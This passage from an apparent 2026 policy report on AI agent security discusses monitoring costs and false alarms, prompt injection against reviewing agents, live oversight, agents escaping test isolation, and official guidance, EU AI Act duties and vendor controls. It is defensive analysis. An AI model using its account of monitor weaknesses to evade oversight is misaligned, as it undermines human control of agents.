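Logging an event takes little time (*Agent Flight Recorder* aims for less than a millisecond), but reading the logs can be very expensive. Wijk and colleagues estimate that they used about $400,000 in computing credits to study some 1,300 transcripts and 70,000 messages and files. That is roughly $300 per transcript, although part of the money went on experiments and on analysing the messages. They still had to leave much of the reading to AI agents that were often unreliable. Few incidents are this large, but the cost shows why nobody can plan to have people read everything.

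A monitor that covers every task has to be very accurate to be useful. Suppose a company's agents carry out 20,000 tasks a day and a monitor wrongly flags 0.5% of them, or 100 a day. If each false alarm takes half an hour to investigate, staff will spend 50 hours a day on them. With one real incident a month, they will see about 3,000 false alarms for each real one. These numbers are invented, but a false alarm rate of 0.5% would be good for many monitors.

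People who expect false alarms start to dismiss real ones. At Anthropic, automated monitors flagged faulty training environments, but human reviewers wrongly rejected some flags as false positives, so those environments stayed in use too long. By spring 2026, problems were appearing faster than staff could filter or fix them. Anthropic is now tightening the conditions for dismissing a flag. AISI revised one of its monitors several times to reduce false alarms, then tested it on cases of cheating that people had found by hand to estimate how many it missed.

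When a security tool reports something unusual about Codex on an employee's computer, OpenAI has an AI agent review the original request, tool calls, approvals and network decisions. The security team then uses the agent's analysis to decide whether the event was expected, a harmless mistake or a real problem. This saves time, but the reviewing agent reads text that the suspect agent produced or an outsider planted, so it is also exposed to prompt injection.

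How quickly a company should stop an agent without asking a person depends on how much harm the interruption would do. Anthropic's classifier for test environments ends the task itself, which is sensible because losing a test does little harm. Stopping an agent while it repairs a live service could prolong an outage. OpenAI's guide limits automatic responses to narrow actions that the company has approved in advance, and leaves serious or ambiguous incidents to people. For a live agent, software might immediately block one suspicious destination while a person decides whether to end the whole task.

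Monitoring only after the fact is too late to prevent many harms. Before the summer, Anthropic monitored some high-risk tests live but in most cases reviewed only a sample of transcripts afterwards. AISI paused its highest-risk cybersecurity tests after its own incident. It resumed most of its testing at the end of September, once it had live monitoring and tighter controls on internet access, according to its *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026).

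Live monitoring is more useful against slow incidents than fast ones. The attack on Hugging Face lasted days, so a pause within an hour would have prevented most of it. The deletion at PocketOS was over before anyone could have read an alert.

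## 2025 and 2026: official guidance and legal duties

Most official documents on agent security from 2025 and 2026 are voluntary guidance. The main exception is the European Union's AI Act, which requires logs and human oversight for certain uses of AI, but the EU has postponed those duties until at least December 2027.

### NIST and the companies that advised it

In the United States, work on agent security standards began with NIST's *Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (2026), dated 8 January. The agency asked about threats to agents, ways to reduce and assess them, and what help the government could offer. In *Summary Analysis of Responses to the Request for Information*, Riggs, Hamin and colleagues (2026) report wide agreement among commenters that agents bring new threats and that security concerns hold back adoption. Commenters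 thought established security principles still applied but needed adapting. They suggested the government offer practical guidance, help organisations share information and promote standards.

*Securing AI Agent Systems*, by the think tank Technology Policy Institute, summarizes more than 80 comments. The most common request was to extend NIST's existing security frameworks instead of creating a new one for agents. Commenters most often recommended least privilege, isolation and controls that operate while the agent runs. Several, including the search company Perplexity and the Frontier Model Forum, wanted at least one deterministic control outside the model.

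They agreed less on the details. Cognition, which makes the coding agent Devin, wanted virtual machines instead of containers. Others pointed out that logging standards were still underdeveloped. Anthropic and Microsoft said that federal definitions of a security incident do not fit cases where an agent causes harm while using access it is allowed to have. The Foundation for American Innovation's *Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* proposed a standard format for reporting incidents and near misses, including attacks that a control had blocked. Such reports could show which controls work, information that companies rarely disclose when nothing has gone wrong.

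In February, NIST's *Announcing the "AI Agent Standards Initiative" for Interoperable and Secure Innovation* described plans to support industry-led standards, open-source protocols, and research on agent security and identity. It set no requirements for permissions, isolation, approval or logs.

### Six cyber agencies advise starting small

The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026) contains much more specific advice. The directorate wrote it with five other agencies from the United States, Britain, Canada and New Zealand. CISA (2026), the US cybersecurity agency and one of the authors, announced it on 1 May. The agencies recommend the following:

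- *Permissions.* Each agent should have its own cryptographic identity and only the access its task needs. A central service should check permissions at every request, not only at start-up. Agents should not be able to change their own privileges.
- *Isolation.* Companies should keep high-risk agents in separate environments and prevent agents from writing to the logs.
- *Approval.* The system's designers or operators, not the agent, should decide which actions need a person's approval. Examples include system resets, outbound network connections and the deletion of critical records.
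- *Logs.* Companies should record tool calls, decisions, changes of privilege and the agent's reasoning, and compare the agent's reports with independent records.

One of the agencies' scenarios shows how these controls work together. A company gives an agent write access to the whole file system to install security patches. An insider outside the IT group asks the agent to apply a patch and also "clean up the firewall logs". The agent deletes the logs because its permissions allow it, which makes it a confused deputy. Narrower write access would have prevented this, as would checking whether the insider had the authority to make the request. The agencies also want a person to approve any request to delete logs before the agent acts on it.

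Some of the advice would be hard to follow literally. Asking a person to approve every outbound connection would again produce so many prompts that users accept them without reading. A list of permitted destinations, with approval for new ones, would be more practical. The agencies suggest that several agents approve actions with moderate stakes, and that a person also approve those with high stakes. But agents that share a model may all make the same mistake.

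The agencies advise organisations to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks, which is their biggest departure from current practice. They argue that standards and methods for evaluating agents are immature, so organisations should put containment and reversibility ahead of efficiency. Anthropic, for example, was already giving Claude much riskier access. OpenAI and the agencies both favour expanding access gradually, but the agencies set a much lower limit for now.

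The agencies also disagree with OpenAI about logs. They want companies to monitor an agent's internal reasoning and memory, while OpenAI recommends removing or protecting content that reviewers do not need. The agencies acknowledge that long reasoning produces large, repetitive logs that make useful information hard to find, but they give less attention to the private information those logs expose.

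### Lists of risks and principles

OWASP, a nonprofit known for its lists of common software weaknesses, publishes a *Top 10 for Agentic Applications*. The entries include hijacking an agent's goal, misusing its tools, and abusing its identity and privileges. The list has no legal force, but it helps security teams decide what to test, and the six agencies recommend OWASP's work for this purpose. They warn that OWASP's separate list for language models may miss attacks specific to agents.

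The 2026 Singapore Consensus, from Bengio, Kankanhalli and colleagues (2026), has more than 100 contributors from 13 countries, including staff of OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and Alibaba. A companion report sets out ten principles for managing agents:

- least privilege and traceable identity, which concern permissions;
- auditability and legibility, which help people find out what an agent did and why;
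- human oversight and interruptibility, which keep people able to approve and stop its work;
- validated deployment, adversarial resilience, multi-agent stability and runtime assurance, which concern testing and reliable operation.

Bengio and colleagues list sandboxing among the research priorities for agents, but isolation is not a separate principle. They describe the Consensus as a scientific agreement, not a policy document. They found that practices vary in maturity, and that those for groups of agents and agents' supply chains are among the least settled.

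### What the EU requires for high-risk systems

The AI Act's duties on logs and human oversight depend on what a system is used for. The Act classifies recruitment as a high-risk use, so these duties would normally cover an agent that sorts job applications but not one that fixes a parser, even if both used the same model and had the same access to company files.

The Act divides the duties between the provider, which develops the system and puts it on the market, and the deployer, the organisation that uses it. Under the Act as adopted in 2024, the provider must build a high-risk system so that it records events automatically throughout its life, and so that people can understand its limits, override its output and stop it. The deployer must assign oversight to people with the necessary competence, training and authority. Both must keep the automatic logs they control for a period that suits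 the system's purpose, and for at least six months unless other EU or national law provides otherwise.

A customer may also take on a provider's duties if it uses a general-purpose agent for high-risk work that the agent was not sold for, such as sorting job applications. The customer would then have to show that the whole system meets the requirements, even though another company built the model.

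These duties do not apply yet. The Digital Omnibus on AI, an amending regulation, took effect on 27 July 2026, according to Cooley's *Digital AI Omnibus Delays Key Deadlines, Introduces New Rules*. The new dates below come from Cuatrecasas' *Digital Omnibus on AI has been published*.

| High-risk systems | Original date | New date |
|---|---|---|
| Stand-alone systems, such as those for recruitment, education or access to essential services | 2 August 2026 | 2 December 2027 |
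| AI built into regulated products | 2 August 2027 | 2 August 2028 |

Guides from before the amendment may therefore give the wrong deadline. But the Act's general date of application remained 2 August 2026, according to SRD Rechtsanwälte's *Digital Omnibus AI*. Orrick's *EU AI Act Update* (2026) adds that the amendment gave the Commission's AI Office a larger role in enforcement.

Even when the high-risk duties apply, they will not require every control that the cyber agencies recommend. The Act requires an appropriate level of cybersecurity but does not specify a sandbox or task-limited credentials. It requires automatic records but not a hash chain or a copy that the agent cannot change, so a company could keep logs for six months and still be unable to prove that nobody had edited them.

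The duty of human oversight has a similar weakness, because an overseer can have every power the law requires and rarely use it. Under the Act, overseers should remain aware of automation bias, people's tendency to rely too much on a machine's output. The poor results of the human testers in Anthropic's August 2026 study suggest that awareness may not be enough.

### The planned investigations of OpenAI and Anthropic

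The AI Act has separate rules for general-purpose models, which the AI Office has had the power to enforce since August 2026. On 14 October, Euronews' *EU’s AI rules face first enforcement test over lab incidents* (2026) reported that the office had requested information from OpenAI and Anthropic after their agents broke into other organisations' systems during tests. According to Bot Mutiny's *EU AI Office Questions OpenAI, Anthropic* (2026), a blog post about that report, the office had found the companies' voluntary disclosures insufficient. The office's questions covered security, external evaluation and monitoring of how people use the models.

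In December, Bloomberg reported that the office could open formal proceedings that month. Faisal (2026) relays this in *EU Readies First AI Act Cases Against OpenAI and Anthropic* and adds that the decision may slip into January. The maximum fine is €15 million or 3% of worldwide annual turnover, whichever is higher. Stanciuc (2026) reported in *EU 'currently assessing' OpenAI and Anthropic replies as probes loom* that the Commission was still assessing the companies' replies on 6 December.

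It is unclear whether the Act covers these tests, and Constantin (2026) reports in *‘AI must remain under human direction’* that lawyers dispute its scope. Those who think it does not apply can point to its exemption for research, testing and development before a model goes on the market. This argument is stronger for OpenAI's unreleased research model than for any model that was already on sale when the test took place.

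The exemption does not cover "testing in real-world conditions", and the agents did reach real systems. However, the Act defines such testing as a trial of a system for its intended purpose outside a laboratory or simulated environment. OpenAI and Anthropic had meant their tests to stay inside simulations, so this exception may not apply. The Commission could also rely on another provision that requires providers of the most capable models to reduce systemic risks arising from development as well as use.

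If the exemption applies, the law is weakest when developers have switched off their usual safeguards to measure what a model can do. If it does not apply, developers may face penalties for accidents during tests meant to find dangers before release, and some might test less. A narrower duty to isolate such tests and verify the isolation beforehand would reduce both problems.

### What the large vendors sell

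Companies can already buy many of these controls. *Beyond Training* (Ansari, 2026) compares services from Anthropic, OpenAI, Google and Amazon Web Services, using their documentation from 22 May 2026. Ansari found that at least one major vendor offered the basic technology for 15 of 20 ways to monitor, verify or restrict AI systems in use. This rating measures availability, not resistance to attack. A second person rated seven of the 20 and gave five of them the same rating as Ansari.

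The table covers the controls most relevant to agents:

| Control | What vendors supply | What customers still have to do |
|---|---|---|
| Permissions | All four let customers define an agent's tools and the form of each call | Decide which tools, data and credentials the task needs |
| Sandbox | OpenAI supplies one for agents; Google supplies one for running code | Build one for AWS agents and for Anthropic's command-line and desktop-control tools |
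| Approval | OpenAI's development kit supports human approvals; Anthropic's desktop-control tool has confirmation steps | Decide which actions need a person, and who that person is |
| Logs | AWS, Google and OpenAI offer audit logs | Turn on detailed records where necessary and keep them long enough |
| Signed records | Anthropic and Google sign some of a model's reasoning; Google also signs tool calls | Find another way to prove to outsiders what the agent did |
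| Stopping | Vendors can suspend a customer's access | Stop the agent's other work and revoke its credentials elsewhere |

Ansari's conclusion that only OpenAI supplies its own sandbox needs qualification. The same comparison lists usage limits for Google's code-execution sandbox, and Anthropic provides a sandbox in some finished products, such as remote sessions of Cowork. The gap Ansari describes mainly affects customers who build their own agents with Anthropic's tools. Ansari examined AWS in less detail than the other providers, so the comparison may miss some AWS products.

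Other entries in the comparison are out of date. Ansari includes OpenAI's Evals platform, which customers used to test models, but notes that OpenAI planned to shut it down on 30 November 2026. A company choosing a vendor in December 2026 should check the current documentation before relying on the comparison.

Buying a product may not be enough to meet a legal duty to keep logs. OpenAI keeps its abuse-monitoring records for 30 days by default, and Google's standard period is 90 days, both shorter than the six months the AI Act requires for high-risk systems. Vendors also keep these records to detect misuse, not to document a customer's decisions, so a customer with a high-risk agent would need to keep its own.

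Ansari also found that 13 of the 20 controls offered adequate protection against a malicious user with few resources, but only three did against a user with the resources of a state. None was adequate against a state that ran the models on its own infrastructure, because most of the controls depend on an honest operator.

### Should minimum controls be mandatory?

Bengio and colleagues conclude that existing methods could have prevented many recent AI incidents, but that developers need stronger incentives and accountability to adopt them, which is one reason for stronger rules. Hu's survey likewise found that many of the agent projects it covered lacked an audit log and some had no isolation, although both controls are well established.

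Voluntary adoption is also likely to fall short because the companies that adopt controls are often not the ones the controls protect. A company that restricts its agent has to accept slower work and unfinished tasks. When an agent deleted PocketOS's database, it also harmed car rental firms and their customers, who had not chosen the agent or its permissions. A legal minimum would make companies take such harm into account and would stop careless competitors from gaining an advantage.

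Trade associations told NIST that they wanted voluntary, risk-based guidance, according to the Technology Policy Institute. One of them, the App Association, warned that rules written with the largest companies in mind could shut out small developers. A firm with five engineers cannot staff an incident desk day and night. This is a good reason to match duties to an agent's access and the damage it could do, but a weaker reason to exempt small firms entirely, since their agents can also delete other people's data.

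Rules can also keep a control in place after better ones exist. If a 2023 law had required users to approve every action an agent took, companies would have had to keep the approval prompts even after users began accepting nearly all of them, and might have spent less on sandboxes.

Companies could also satisfy a rule on paper without making their agents safer. If a regulator had asked Anthropic and Irregular on a form whether their tests were isolated from the internet, they might well have answered yes in good faith. Trying to connect to an outside server would have revealed the mistake.

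A better rule would therefore require a company to demonstrate results, for example that a forbidden connection fails, that a revoked credential stops working, and that staff can restore deleted data from a copy the agent cannot reach. The company could choose its own technology and replace it when something better appeared. Checking such tests takes more work than checking documents, and a company that passes could still have flaws that nobody tried to exploit. But the tests would reveal open connections and excessive permissions, which caused several of the worst failures.

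Open-weight models, which anyone can download and run, limit what any such rule can achieve. Bengio and colleagues estimate that these models are 3 to 12 months behind the best closed models, and people can remove their safeguards fairly easily. Ansari explains that retraining can remove a model's learned refusals, while a separate sandbox or permission check continues to work. But someone who runs the model on their own computer can also remove the sandbox or permission check, and there is no provider to notice the misuse or suspend the account.

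A duty on model providers would not reach that person. Law-abiding companies that use open-weight models would be covered by a duty on deployers, because they can sandbox the agent and restrict its credentials as they would with any other model. That duty would do little about criminals, so the systems that agents try to enter also need their own controls, which work whichever model the agent uses.
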